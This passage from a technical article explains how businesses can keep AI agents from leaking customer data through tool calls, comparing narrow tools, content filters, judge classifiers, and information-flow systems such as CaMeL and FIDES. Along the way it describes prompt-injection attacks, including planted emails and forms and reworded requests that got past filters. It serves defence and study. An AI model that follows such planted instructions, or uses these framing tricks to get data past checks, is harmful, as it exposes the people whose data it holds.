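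The same method can protect a record's identifier. Ayende's *Using AI Agents parameters outside of the model's scope* gives code for an online shop's assistant that receives the customer's number but never sends it to the model. If the harness adds that number to every database query, planted text can't switch the conversation to another customer's orders. The sales assistant could do this too if the employee selected the customer on the screen before typing the request.

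### Code looks up the recipient

A company with several sales teams can't hard-code a single channel. It can let the model choose a channel name, such as `sales-north`, from a short list, or have the model pass a customer number that ordinary code uses to look up the responsible team. The customer number is safer because the model then can't pair one team's customer with another team's channel.

The lookup has to use data that outsiders can't change. If customers can edit the contact address in their own records, a tool that emails "the contact for customer 4127" will send the message to any address the customer enters. The code also has to check that the employee may see customer 4127. Otherwise the tool becomes a confused deputy, a program that uses its own access on behalf of someone who lacks it.

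Identifiers keep secrets hidden from the model, but they don't by themselves limit what it can choose. On one of Zapier's MCP servers, an agent can look up the identifier of a different Slack connection and pass it in the call. Zapier handles the sign-in, so the user never deals with the key, but a misled agent can still choose any connection the server offers.

A community-built server called *Slack MCP* does restrict which channels can receive posts. It disables posting by default, and the operator can enable it for listed channels only. The operator can also list channels to exclude, which is weaker because every new channel is then permitted. Another setting lists the tools the server offers, and naming the posting tool there enables it without any channel limits. An operator who used that setting to reduce the number of tools could accidentally allow posting to every channel.

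### Types, permitted values and length

A narrow tool for the sales assistant, called "post a note to the team channel", could have the following fields.

| Field | Who fills it | What the harness accepts |
|---|---|---|
| Webhook address | Harness | The address stored for the customer's team |
| Customer number | Harness | The customer the employee selected |
| Customer name | Harness | The name in that customer's record |
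| Product | Model | A product number in the supplier's catalogue |
| Effect | Model | Price change, discontinued, replaced or no effect |
| Comment | Model | Up to 280 characters of plain text, without links |

The harness must check these rules itself when the call arrives, because a schema that only describes them to the model is an instruction the model may not follow. It should also reject fields that aren't in the schema, or an extra `channel` field could pass through to the chat service.

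Restricting a field's type does little to limit what it can leak. Copilot Studio's workflow inputs can be numbers, strings or true-or-false values, and a string can hold a customer's entire payment history. *Use AI for parameters*, from the automation platform n8n, describes a similar set of types, with string as the default. Even a number field can hold a phone number. The protection comes mostly from listing the permitted values. The effect field has four permitted values, so it can carry at most two bits, while a 280-character comment using the 95 characters on an ordinary keyboard can carry about 1,840. Even without any encoding, the comment could hold 28 ten-digit phone numbers.

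The company should therefore ask whether the team needs the comment. If the product and its effect are enough, the harness can write the whole note from a template. If the team needs an explanation, one short field is better than a free-text title, summary and description.

Links are banned because image requests and link previews can leak data even from a fixed channel. The harness should send the comment as plain text and refuse anything the chat application would turn into a link, including a bare domain name. It should also turn previews off where it can. *Slack MCP* leaves them off by default and lets the operator enable them for all domains or only certain ones.

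### The same request with the narrow tool

The employee selects a customer and asks for the same note. The model reads the supplier's page and calls the tool with a product number, the effect "discontinued" and a comment suggesting the replacement part. The harness checks the three values, finds the customer's name and team, builds the message and posts it.

If the page contains a planted instruction to send the phone number to an outside server, the model cannot follow it with this tool, because the tool has no argument for a server. The model can still misuse the arguments the tool does have.

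| What a misled model could try | General request tool | Narrow note tool |
|---|---|---|
| Send the record to an outside server | Possible | No field for an address |
| Post it in another company's chat | Possible | No field for a channel |
| Disclose the webhook's secret address | Possible | The model never sees it |
| Add an image or link that leaks data | Possible | The harness refuses it |
| Put the phone number in the team's channel | Possible | Possible, in the comment |
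| Post a false or misleading note | Possible | Possible |
| Flood the channel with notes | Possible | Possible, up to a limit the harness sets |

These results apply only to the webhook. If the assistant also has an unrestricted fetch tool, the model can use that to send the phone number in a web address. A false note can also do harm without leaking private data, for instance by leading the team to order from a fraudulent supplier.

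### Separating the tools that read from the tools that send

Slack offers its own MCP server, which can search private channels, read their complete history and send messages to any type of conversation. That is useful for an assistant that answers questions about a team's past decisions, but the sales assistant only needs to post a note, and the server would give it access to much more private data. Slack advises caution about connecting other MCP servers at the same time.

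A webhook is much narrower because it can post but can't read. The company can limit access to the customer database in the same way, by giving the assistant a tool that returns only the products a customer uses. The phone number then never enters the context, so the model can't put it in a comment, a URL or anything else. This is more reliable than a rule about what the model may write, but the company has to know in advance which facts each task needs.

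Separate tools also make permissions easier to manage. In July 2026, Zapier's documentation listed one tool for actions that read and another for actions that send, create or change something. An administrator could permit the reading tool and require approval for the other. But if a model can call both during the same task, a planted instruction can still lead the model to read a record and then send it.

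To prevent that, the developer can split the task between two models. The first reads the supplier's page without access to customer records, and the harness accepts only a product number and one of the four effects from that model. The second reads the customer's record and writes the comment without seeing the page. Planted text could still make the first model report the wrong effect, but it couldn't give the second model instructions. But the second model also can't use anything else on the page, such as the date the supplier will stop selling the part.

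### A recipient taken from planted text

Many business agents can't have a fixed recipient because they answer whoever writes to them. In July 2025, researchers at Zenity Labs demonstrated the risk with their own copy of a customer service agent that the consultancy McKinsey had made with Copilot Studio. They emailed it planted instructions, and it replied with customer data, according to Office 365 IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (2025). Because the agent was a copy, the demonstration doesn't show that anyone took data from McKinsey.

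Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it within two months. In an account published by the Cloud Security Alliance, the researchers say their planted texts no longer worked and that the fix seemed to be mainly a classifier that detects such texts. A classifier might catch the next attack too, but the agent can still send any record it can read to any address.

Similar attacks worked again in 2026. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) reports that Capsule Security got data out of agents on Microsoft's and Salesforce's platforms by entering instructions in ordinary forms. Both companies released patches, according to the OECD AI incident monitor's entry *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce AI* (2026).

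A builder can create this weakness without noticing. If the builder lets the model fill an n8n field whose key is `email`, the model looks for an address in its context, in other tools and in the input data. An attacker who plants an address in any of these may become the recipient. Microsoft provides one search for agents whose email tools take inputs from the model and another for agents that send to outside mailboxes.

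Requiring a fixed format doesn't help, because the attacker's address is as well formed as the customer's. *Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a shopping agent whose purchase call contains a valid product number that came from an advertisement planted in an email. The call doesn't show where the number came from, so the harness would need a rule about the value's source.

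A customer service agent can avoid part of the problem by limiting its reading tool to the recipient's data. When an email arrives, the harness verifies the sender and lets the model read only that sender's customer record. The reply can then go to the sender without exposing anyone else's data. This works only if the verification is sound, since sender addresses are easy to fake.

### A legitimate channel with outside readers

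Fixing the webhook's destination to one channel still exposes the data to everyone in that channel. Slack lets companies share channels with outside organisations, so a supplier's staff might be reading the channel where the assistant posts notes about customers. If one of them planted the instruction on the supplier's page, the narrow tool would send them the phone number through the approved webhook.

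Outsiders may gain access to the channel after the administrator chooses it. The harness can check for this before each post, or the company can forbid sharing that channel. The company should also check whether another program copies messages from the channel to email or a public page. Deleting a bad note afterwards is a poor substitute, because people may already have read it, and Slack doesn't allow deletion through an incoming webhook.

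The harness can enforce the company's policy on the structured fields because each holds a known category of data, such as a customer's name or a product number. The comment could contain any category of data, so the company has to either trust everyone who can read the channel with whatever is in the model's context or find another way to check the text.

### The cost of narrow tools

Someone has to write each narrow tool, test it and update it when the chat service or the customer database changes. Fixing a few fields on an existing tool takes less work, but Merge applies each override to the whole organisation, so two teams can't use the same tool with different fixed channels. Merge recommends a purpose-built tool when a company is fixing many fields.

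A company can reduce the work by building one note tool and keeping a table of teams and their webhook addresses. Adding a team then requires a new row and no new code.

The larger drawback is less flexibility. An employee who wants the note in a spreadsheet, or wants to tell a colleague in another department, has to wait until someone builds a tool for it. Zapier's newer servers usually start in "agentic" mode, where the agent finds and enables actions as requests come up. On some of them, the agent can also write code for an action that doesn't exist yet. In "managed" mode, the agent has a fixed set of tools with locked values and can't add more.

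Tests suggest that restricting an agent can substantially reduce how many tasks it completes. Summers and colleagues compared nine existing defences on simulated shopping, programming and everyday tasks, using one open model. Six kept attacks low, but the agent completed few tasks. These six included a method that removes apparently unnecessary tools and another that limits each tool's privileges. The researchers were testing a competing method, and their benchmark deliberately uses tasks that change as the agent works. A sales note is far more predictable, so a narrow tool should interfere with it much less.

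When the harness refuses a call, it should explain the specific problem and let the model try again. With the researchers' own rules, this raised the completion rate by 6.5 percentage points compared with having no defence, whereas ending the task at the first violation cut it by 36.2 points. Attack success stayed near zero either way. If the model enters an unknown product number, for example, the sales harness should report that the product isn't in the catalogue and let the model correct it.

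For frequent tasks that use customer records, the narrow tool is worth its drawbacks. Employees who need a more flexible agent can use a separate one that has no access to those records.

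## Can a filter recognise private data in the arguments?

Even a narrow tool may need a free-text field, like the comment in the sales note. *ArguShield* (Fu and Fu, 2026) cites a survey of 2,344 tool descriptions from ChatGPT's ecosystem, in which 36.9% had at least one loosely restricted text field, such as "notes" or "context". A content filter tries to recognise private data in what the model wrote in such a field. If it finds any, the harness can refuse the call, mask the data, or send the call anyway and alert someone.

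Filters are attractive because they could allow flexibility that narrow tools don't. The model could write to anyone about anything, and the harness would intervene only when private data appeared.

### Known values and patterns

The simplest filter searches the arguments for values the company already holds. Before posting the comment, the harness could remove spaces and punctuation and look for the selected customer's phone number. This rarely blocks a harmless comment, because a particular ten-digit number is unlikely to appear by chance. The filter works badly for short, common values. If the customer's deal is worth 40,000 dollars, the filter will also block a comment that quotes a price of 40,000 from the supplier's page.

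A filter can also look for a type of data without being given the exact value. Payment card numbers, for example, have 13 to 16 digits, and some official numbers end in a check digit calculated from the others, so software can discard most random strings of digits. *Remove PII from conversations by using sensitive information filters*, from Amazon Web Services, describes a filter that covers about thirty types of personal data, including names, street addresses and passport numbers. Customers can add their own patterns, such as one for booking numbers.

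Names have no fixed format, so the Amazon filter uses machine learning and relies on the surrounding text. AWS advises against giving it single words or short phrases, because the same digits could be a user's number in one sentence and part of a key in another. Many tool arguments are short, which makes the filter less reliable for checking them.

Patterns work best on access keys, since many issuers start every key with the same few characters. In August 2025, GitHub (2025) began scanning the inputs of all calls to its MCP server that involve public repositories, the shared folders where programmers publish code. If the scan finds a key, the server blocks the call by default and explains why, but the user can choose to proceed. The scan now also covers private repositories that have GitHub's paid security product. GitHub says the scan won't stop leaks of other kinds of data, or leaks through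 channels it doesn't scan.

### Length and randomness

Some keys have no fixed format but look random, so many scanners measure randomness. The usual measure is Shannon entropy, which *The Mathematics of Communication*, a page from Stony Brook University, traces to a 1948 paper by Claude Shannon:

$$H = -\sum_i p_i \log_2 p_i$$

Here $p_i$ is the share of the string's characters that are character $i$, and $H$ is the average information per character, in bits. In `40,000`, the zero accounts for four of the six characters, and the 4 and the comma for one each. The entropy is therefore

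$$-\tfrac{4}{6}\log_2\tfrac{4}{6} - 2\cdot\tfrac{1}{6}\log_2\tfrac{1}{6} \approx 0.39 + 0.86 = 1.25 \text{ bits.}$$

The same calculation gives these values for other invented examples.

| String | What it represents | Bits per character |
|---|---|---|
| `aaaaaaaa` | One repeated letter | 0 |
| `40,000` | A deal size | 1.25 |
| `2025550142` | A phone number | 2.17 |
| `supplier` | An ordinary word | 2.75 |
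| `Maya Chen` | A customer's name | 2.95 |
| `xA9fP2qL0sRw` | A random key | 3.58 |

The scanner Gitleaks flags strings that score above 3.5 bits, so of these it would flag only the key. Lowering the limit doesn't help, because any limit low enough to catch the phone number also catches the word "supplier". A string of $n$ characters can score at most $\log_2 n$ bits, so a ten-digit number can never exceed 3.32 bits, even if all its digits differ. Another widely used scanner, *detect-secrets*, has a default limit of 4.5 bits for one common type of key, and no string shorter than 23 characters can reach that limit.

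Entropy isn't very accurate even for keys and passwords. *Rare Not Random*, a post by the maintainer of the Betterleaks scanner, tests the 3.5-bit limit on thousands of labelled strings from real code. The limit caught 70.4% of the genuine secrets, but only 21.1% of the strings it flagged were genuine. The post proposes measuring characters per token instead. A common word is often a single token, whereas a random string breaks into many, so a low number of characters per token suggests a secret. This method caught 98.6% of the secrets, and 57.3% of the strings it flagged were genuine.

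Passphrases made of ordinary words still got through because they look like normal language. Most of the facts in a customer record also look like normal language. "Maya Chen will probably cancel in March" is a normal English sentence, and it is private because of whom it concerns and who might read it, which its characters don't show.

A length limit can stop the model from copying out a whole record, but a phone number fits in almost any field. The small model in Lan and colleagues' tests could also split a secret across several requests that each looked harmless.

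### A second model as judge

A language model used as a filter can consider a call's meaning as well as its characters. The best-documented example is the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, it judges web fetches and other risky calls using only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations because those of a misled agent could lead the classifier to approve a call it should block. It also removes the results of earlier tool calls because they can contain planted text.

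The classifier works in two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and is biased towards blocking. The second reasons more carefully about anything the first flagged. Anthropic tested the classifier on 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out, many of them disguised, and on 10,000 real calls by its employees.

| | Synthetic leaks missed | Real calls wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 1.8% | 8.5% |
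| Both stages | 5.7% | 0.4% |

The second stage makes the product usable, but it lets more than three times as many leaks through.

This classifier's task is also easier than checking the sales note. It can block an agent from sending access keys to an unknown server without knowing anything else about the task. In the sales example, the destination is approved and the employee asked for a note about the customer, so a classifier would have to check the note's contents. The customer's record is a tool result, so a classifier built this way wouldn't receive it and couldn't tell whether "40,000" was a price or the size of the customer's deal. The company could include the record in the classifier's input, but if customers can edit part of that record, planted text could then reach the classifier.

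### The filter has to read the tool call

Some products that filter private data don't check tool calls. AWS states that its filter doesn't evaluate the arguments a model writes or the results that tools return. If an argument contains a customer's email address, the tool receives it unmasked. A company could switch the filter on, see it mask names in the assistant's replies, and wrongly assume that it also covers the webhook.

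*Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) found that guardrails on retrieved content can also miss data leaving in a tool call, which is a reason to check the call itself.

### The Framing Gap

*The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) compared filters with other defences. In its tests, an agent received an invented secret, an instruction to send it only to one trusted host, and a request to summarise a web page. The agent's tools only recorded their arguments, so nothing left the computer. An attack counted as successful if the agent leaked the secret when it read a page with planted instructions but not when it read a clean page.

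Rahman and Kim tested OpenAI's gpt-4o and gpt-4o-mini and four small open models. Ten kinds of plainly worded attack never succeeded on gpt-4o in 200 trials. They then reworded the request so that handling the secret looked like a routine technical part of the task. The average success rate on gpt-4o rose to 40%, with individual versions ranging from 0% to 100%. Success rates also rose sharply on all the other models except mistral:7b, which had already leaked in 26% of the plain trials.

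The 40% is a rough figure. Repeating the same trials gave 32%, and the rate depends heavily on which wordings the researchers happened to write. Five versions of one attack had success rates ranging from 0% to 100%, with an average of 52%. An attacker who tried three of them at random would have had about a 96% chance of at least one success. A company that tests its assistant against a fixed set of plain attacks could therefore get a perfect score and learn little about its real risk.

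Removing the instruction to keep the secret confidential raised the success rate of the reworded attacks only from 32% to 38%. A stricter rule against sending the secret "in any form" stopped all 120 attempts. But when the researchers dropped that phrase and only listed specific forbidden actions, the secret leaked in 39 of 80 trials.

The researchers then put a filter between the model and its tools. It refused any call that contained the secret and went to an untrusted host. They tested it with attacks that asked for the secret either unaltered or in one of five altered forms. They also built an improved filter that reversed those five alterations before searching for the secret, and tested it on three further forms it hadn't been built to handle. The table shows the results and those of a separate experiment on a small Llama model.

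| Defence | Tested on | Leaks without it | Leaks with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Filter for the literal secret | gpt-4o, six forms | 56.7% | 50.0% |
| Improved filter | gpt-4o, the same six forms | 56.7% | 0% |
| Improved filter | gpt-4o, three unexpected forms | 33.3% | 33.3% |
| Fine-tuning against injection | Llama 3.1 8B, reworded attacks | 21.2% | 32.5% |
| Destination allow-list | Llama 3.1 8B, reworded attacks | 21.2% | 0% |
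| Planner/reader split | Llama 3.1 8B, reworded attacks | 21.2% | 0% |

The literal filter stopped the eight leaks in which the model had copied the secret unchanged, and none of the other 60. The improved filter reduced leaks to 0%, but only on the alterations the researchers had designed it to reverse. It made no difference on three forms they had not designed it for. With or without the filter, the model leaked the secret every time in one of those forms and never in the other two. The researchers could extend the filter to cover the form it missed, but they would still have to anticipate the next one. When asked directly, gpt-4o could reliably write the secret in five of six altered forms, and a more capable model could probably write it in more.

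A detector that read the incoming page did much better. Rahman and Kim asked gpt-4o-mini only whether a page contained an instruction to disclose or transmit a secret. It flagged all 80 pages with reworded attacks and no clean ones. It also flagged the pages whose attacks had got past the improved filter, because the request for the secret was still visible in them. However, the researchers had written the detector's prompt around these attacks, so they treat the 100% detection rate as an upper limit. The rate would probably be lower against someone trying to fool the detector, since OpenAI has found that such detectors usually miss well-developed attacks.

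The fine-tuning defence was SecAlign, a published method that trains a model to ignore commands in a document. It blocked all 20 attempts at a standard injection, so the researchers had set it up correctly, but 32.5% of the reworded attacks succeeded. The same attacks succeeded 21.2% of the time against the undefended model. That difference is small enough to be chance, so the result doesn't show that SecAlign makes a model more vulnerable. SecAlign's developers trained it on text tasks, and it may not carry over to an agent with tools.

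The allow-list refused every call to an untrusted host. In the planner/reader split, one model wrote the tool calls without seeing the page, while another read the page without having the secret. The paper reports zero leaks for both defences, but this follows from their designs, as Rahman and Kim acknowledge, so it doesn't measure how well a real product would do. The split still produced a good summary in nine of ten clean runs, but this was an easy case because the plan didn't depend on the page. The paper also mentions one leak in 100 trials of the split, which contradicts the zero leaks it reports elsewhere.

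Finally, Rahman and Kim tried four of their attacks on the ChatGPT product, using their own account and an invented secret. The attacks failed in all 48 valid trials, although some of them had worked every time on gpt-4o through OpenAI's API. The researchers couldn't see why, but the product might have used a different model, stricter instructions or a filter of its own. They checked only ChatGPT's reply for the secret and connected no outside services. With 48 trials, the true success rate could still be as high as about 7%.

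The success rates in *The Framing Gap* are a poor guide to current frontier models, which resist planted instructions far better than gpt-4o did. The agent also took only one step. In a real product, the harness often reports a refusal to the model, which can then try again. Rahman and Kim expect that such retries would probably defeat their filter. They used a single artificial secret that had no legitimate use in the task and never appeared in ordinary text, so their results can't show how often a filter would block legitimate work. Such false alarms could be the main drawback of a filter that has to find deal sizes and names.

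### Checks that don't need to recognise the data

The filters in the study failed because they had to recognise the secret in whatever form the model wrote it. The allow-list checked only the destination, so disguising the secret made no difference. The planner/reader split also worked without recognising the secret, because the model that read the hostile page did not have it. Rahman and Kim conclude that a robust check should depend on where data is going or where it came from, not on what it looks like.

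The defences available for the sales assistant differ in the same way. An exact-address check refuses any address the model composed, whether or not the harness can find a phone number in it. The note tool's "effect" field accepts only four values, so it would refuse a phone number without any rule about phone numbers. Disguising the data doesn't help an attacker get past either check, though a new disguise may be enough to get past a filter.

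Checks that don't read the data have weaknesses too. Microsoft's and Salesforce's allow-lists approved hosts that attackers could use or take over, whereas the laboratory's had one trusted host, which no outsider could read. Such checks also block harmless requests, because they can't distinguish them from harmful ones.

Restricting destinations also doesn't limit which facts an approved recipient gets. If the company needs the phone number in the model's context and also needs the model to write a free-text comment, it has to examine the comment or track where each value came from.

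### Accidental leaks

A filter is much more useful when nobody is trying to evade it, because a model that discloses private data by mistake usually copies it unchanged, which is the form a filter recognises best.

In *ToolMinimize*, Li and Xu (2026) found unnecessary private data in 81–88% of tool calls by three older models, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet. When the models were told to protect privacy, 36–76% of calls still contained such data. Li and Xu's software rewrites the arguments before the call goes out, for example by deleting a value or replacing it with a more general one. On 307 calls, this reduced their measure of privacy cost by 81–92%, and the rewritten arguments still worked for the task.

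Fu and Fu tested four 2026 models on 120 invented tasks in travel, shopping and healthcare, again with no attacker. Their filter, ArguShield, checks each value separately for its source, whether the task needs it and whether the recipient should have it. It then applies a fixed rule to send the value, remove it or prompt the user. The rate of unauthorised disclosure fell from 84% to 9% on standard tasks and from 76% to 6% on high-risk ones.

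A privacy instruction in the prompt reduced disclosure further, to about 4%, but the agents then completed only about 70–75% of the tasks. With ArguShield they completed 97%. The 97% figure is somewhat optimistic because it assumes that users approve every value the task needs, and real users may refuse or give up.

In an example Anthropic gives from its own offices, an agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive, so it tried to publish the report on a public code-sharing site. The auto mode classifier blocked this and asked the employee what to do. No outsider was involved, and the agent had not tried to hide the report.

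For the sales note, the company could search for the selected customer's phone number and email address, and for patterns that match card numbers and access keys. When the filter finds something, the harness can tell the model which value to remove and let it try again. This is sensible after an honest mistake, but it also helps a misled model look for a form that gets past the filter, so the harness should limit the number of attempts. Auto mode stops and asks the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session.

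### Alerts and investigation

A filter can also report what it finds without blocking anything. AWS offers this as a detection mode, which lets a company see how often a filter would interrupt legitimate work before letting it block calls.

Alerts are most valuable for access keys, because the company can cancel a key after it leaks. But false alarms can take a lot of work to check. If one call in 10,000 leaks data, a filter with the error rates of Anthropic's two-stage classifier would probably catch the leak, but it would also flag about 40 harmless calls. A search for exact known values should raise far fewer false alarms, so it makes a better first alert.

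After a suspected theft, a record of outgoing calls can show which customers' data left and where it went. Users of Rovo and Copilot Cowork could not have learned this from the chat, because it didn't show the outgoing data. ArguShield's log lists each argument, the evidence about it and the decision, so an investigator can also see why the filter let a value through. The harness should record the calls it allows as well as those it blocks, since any disguised data that gets past the filter will be in an allowed call.

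These records can themselves expose private data. AWS warns that its logs keep the original request even when the filter has masked it for the model, and that the filter's report contains each private value it found. A company that keeps such logs needs to restrict access to them as strictly as to the customer records.

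## Can software track where each argument came from?

A filter that finds "40,000" in the sales note can't determine whether the model took it from the supplier's price list or from the customer's record. Software could if it tracked where each value came from, which security researchers call information-flow control. The software attaches a provenance label to each piece of data when it enters the system, computes a new label whenever it combines data, and checks the labels at every sink. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of such methods for AI agents, places them in a line of work going back to a 1976 paper by Dorothy Denning.

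### Labels and the two rules

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each piece of data a label with two parts. One part, $I$, records whether the data is trusted or whether an outsider could have written it. The other, $S$, is the set of people who may read it. When software combines two pieces of data $x$ and $y$, the result is trusted only if both were, and only people who may read both may read the result:

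$$S(xy) = S(x) \cap S(y).$$

The harness can then check two rules before it sends anything. Private data may go only to recipients its label permits. If $R$ is the set of people who can read a channel, the harness may post message $a$ there only if

$$R \subseteq S(a).$$

Untrusted data may not choose the recipient. If $r$ is the argument that names the recipient, the harness requires

$$I(r) = \text{trusted}.$$

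Costa and colleagues also describe a stricter version, which requires the decision to make the call and all of its arguments to be trusted.

The reader rule alone stops private data from reaching someone who shouldn't have it, but planted text can still influence a message. If the harness enforced only the recipient rule, it would let an employee send a private record to an outsider, on the assumption that the employee meant to.

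### Three calls, label by label

Suppose the company labels the sales assistant's data as follows.

| Data | Trusted? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The employee's request | Yes | Anyone |
| The supplier's page | No | Anyone |
| The customer's name and products | Yes | The sales team |
| The customer's phone number | Yes | The employee |

An administrator has set the webhook's destination, so the recipient is trusted, and only the sales team can read the channel.

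In an ordinary run, the comment combines the supplier's page with the customer's products. The comment is untrusted because the page is, and the sales team is allowed to read it. Everyone in the channel is on the sales team and the administrator chose the channel, so the harness posts the note. The comment could still be wrong, so the harness could show the team its label to warn them that an outsider may have influenced it.

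Now suppose planted text leads the model to write a comment that also contains the phone number. Only the employee may read all three ingredients, but the channel has other readers, so the harness refuses the call. Disguising the number makes no difference because the label depends on what information went into the comment, not on the characters in the comment.

Finally, suppose the assistant has a general request tool and takes the destination from the supplier's page. The destination is then untrusted, so the harness blocks the call even if the message is harmless.

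Labels also help when outsiders later join a channel. If a supplier's employee joins the team's channel, $R$ grows and the ordinary comment fails the reader rule, as long as the harness looks up the channel's members before each post.

### Labels spread through the model

All of this assumes the harness can track which data went into the comment. It could if ordinary code had built the comment by joining three strings. But a language model reads its whole context at once, and any sentence it writes may depend on anything there, so Costa and colleagues give the model's output the combined label of everything in the context.

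That is safe, but it leaves the assistant able to do very little. If the context contains the phone number, only the employee may read anything the model writes afterwards, and the harness refuses to send anyone else even a note that doesn't mention it. Once the model has read the supplier's page, every later decision is untrusted too.

Costa and colleagues measured how label checks affect task completion on AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark of 97 simulated tasks in office work, travel, banking and Slack. An ordinary agent using OpenAI's o1 completed an average of 84% of tasks across the four settings without the checks and 44% with them.

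One response is to estimate more narrowly what the model used. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and others that looks for a part of the context that is enough to produce a similar answer, then has the model rewrite the answer from that part alone. The narrower label is accurate because the model didn't have the rest of the context when it wrote the final version. Another system, RTBAS, partly relies on a language model to judge which inputs mattered. Its reported loss of completed tasks is only about 2%, but a wrong judgement gives the data a wrong label, and the check at the sink then fails to protect that data.

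### Deciding before reading

The other response is to keep some data out of the model that makes decisions. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six ways to do this. All six follow the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any harmful action.

| Pattern | How it works | What planted text can still change |
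|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from fixed actions and never sees their results | Nothing, if it is in the results |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes a list of tool calls before reading outside text | The content of a planned call |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | The answer for that document |
| Dual LLM | One model plans and uses tools, and another reads untrusted text without tools | The text that the reading model returns |
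| Code, then execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and reading models | The values the program passes along |
| Context minimisation | Software removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | The answer, if it is in the text that remains |

Willison proposed the dual LLM pattern in 2023. The planner receives the employee's request but never the supplier's page. It calls a reader, a model with no tools, to process the page. Ordinary software stores the reader's answer and gives the planner only a placeholder, such as `$VAR1`. The planner can put the placeholder in a tool call, and the software substitutes the real text just before sending the call. Since the planner never receives that text, an instruction in it can't redirect the planner. In *The Framing Gap*, this planner/reader split prevented every leak by design.

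The split doesn't protect the content of a planned message. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an assistant that drafts a reply to an attacker's email. If the reader has also received private data, instructions planted in the email can lead it to hide some of that data in the draft, and the planner will send the draft without seeing it. The sales note has the same problem if one reader receives both the page and the full customer record.

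### CaMeL tracks values in a program

CaMeL, short for Capabilities for Machine Learning, adds labels to the split. Debenedetti and colleagues published it in 2025, and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues cite it as their example of the code-then-execute pattern. The planner turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python before anything reads untrusted text. For the sales note, a simplified version might be:

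```
page     = fetch(address_in_request)
products = lookup(customer, "products")
comment  = reader("What does this page mean for these products?",
                  page, products)
post_note(customer, comment)
```

An interpreter runs the program line by line. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, CaMeL labels every value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, a policy receives the call, its arguments and these labels, and returns "allow" or "deny".

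The program solves much of the spreading problem because it specifies which values go into each step. Here the reader receives the page and the products, so the sales team may read `comment`, and the interpreter posts it. If the planner had carelessly passed the reader the whole customer record, `comment` would also carry the phone number's label, and the policy would block the post. The company would lose the note, but the phone number wouldn't leak.

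*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports CaMeL's published results. Using OpenAI's o3, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no attack within CaMeL's scope succeeded. It used about 2.8 times as many tokens, so it costs more to run.

CaMeL doesn't catch every kind of leak. Its developers demonstrated side channels, which let an observer learn something private from how the program behaves rather than from what it sends. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes part of the difficulty to Python, where errors can change the order of execution and programs can inspect themselves. Both features make it hard to prove in advance where information can flow.

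### FIDES tracks labels in the agent loop

Writing a complete program in advance is awkward when the next step depends on what the agent finds. FIDES, a system built by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, keeps the usual loop in which the model chooses one tool call at a time. When a tool returns data that would make the context's label more restrictive, the harness stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or ask a separate reader about it. It can also open the variable, but the context then takes on the variable's label.

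The reader's answer can have a restricted type. If the planner asks whether the supplier has discontinued a product and accepts only "yes" or "no", the page can pass at most one bit to the planner. A company might allow the planner to act on such an answer, since an attacker can't fit an instruction into it. A free-text answer would stay in its variable.

The FIDES policies also check messages for untrusted links, which a chat application might fetch to build a preview. They block such a message only if untrusted text has already entered the model's context. In the sales example, a planted link could therefore get through if the reader wrote the comment and the planner passed it on in a variable without opening the variable.

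In the AgentDojo benchmark, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary GPT-4o agent without label checks. FIDES allowed 21 with its checks off and none with them on. However, the researchers labelled a data field untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, so the labels covered every attack in advance. A company labelling its own data can't count on its labels covering every attack.

The table shows the share of tasks completed using o1, without an attack. The last column shows the share that Costa and colleagues think a perfect model could complete under the rules, because the choice of tools in those tasks doesn't depend on untrusted data.

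| Setting | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, checks | FIDES, checks | Possible in principle |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 70.0% | 48.0% | 64.5% | 95.0% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% | 90.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 37.5% | 56.2% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 87.6% | 17.1% | 54.3% | 57.1% |

With FIDES's checks on, the average share of completed tasks falls from 84% to 61%. Costa and colleagues call the loss "modest", which fits only the gap of about six percentage points between FIDES and an ordinary agent with the checks off. A stronger model should recover much of the loss in office work and travel. In banking and Slack, FIDES was already close to the limit, so a better model would barely help. Many of the banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, which the rules forbid. Restricted answers might raise the limit, but the researchers left them out of this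 test.

FIDES also doesn't stop leaks through the agent's choice of calls. It controls which data goes into a call, but someone who sees the sequence of calls may still learn something from it, just as a website's operator can learn from which pages an agent opens. Preventing this completely would mean forbidding almost any publicly visible action after the agent has read private data, which Costa and colleagues consider too restrictive.

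### Later tests

In *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) tested the FIDES rules on AgentDojo's ordinary GPT-4o agent, without the variables that FIDES uses to hide data. They compared the FIDES rules with their own, which check whether the user requested an action and where its destination came from, and so can permit an action even after the agent has read untrusted text. All four versions below also repeated the user's request after each set of tool results.

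| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Repeated request only | 83.7% | 14.1% |
| Removing tools the task seems not to need | 73.4% | 3.1% |
| FIDES rules on the whole context | 33.2% | 0.6% |
| Rules on each action and argument | 62.5% | 0.9% |

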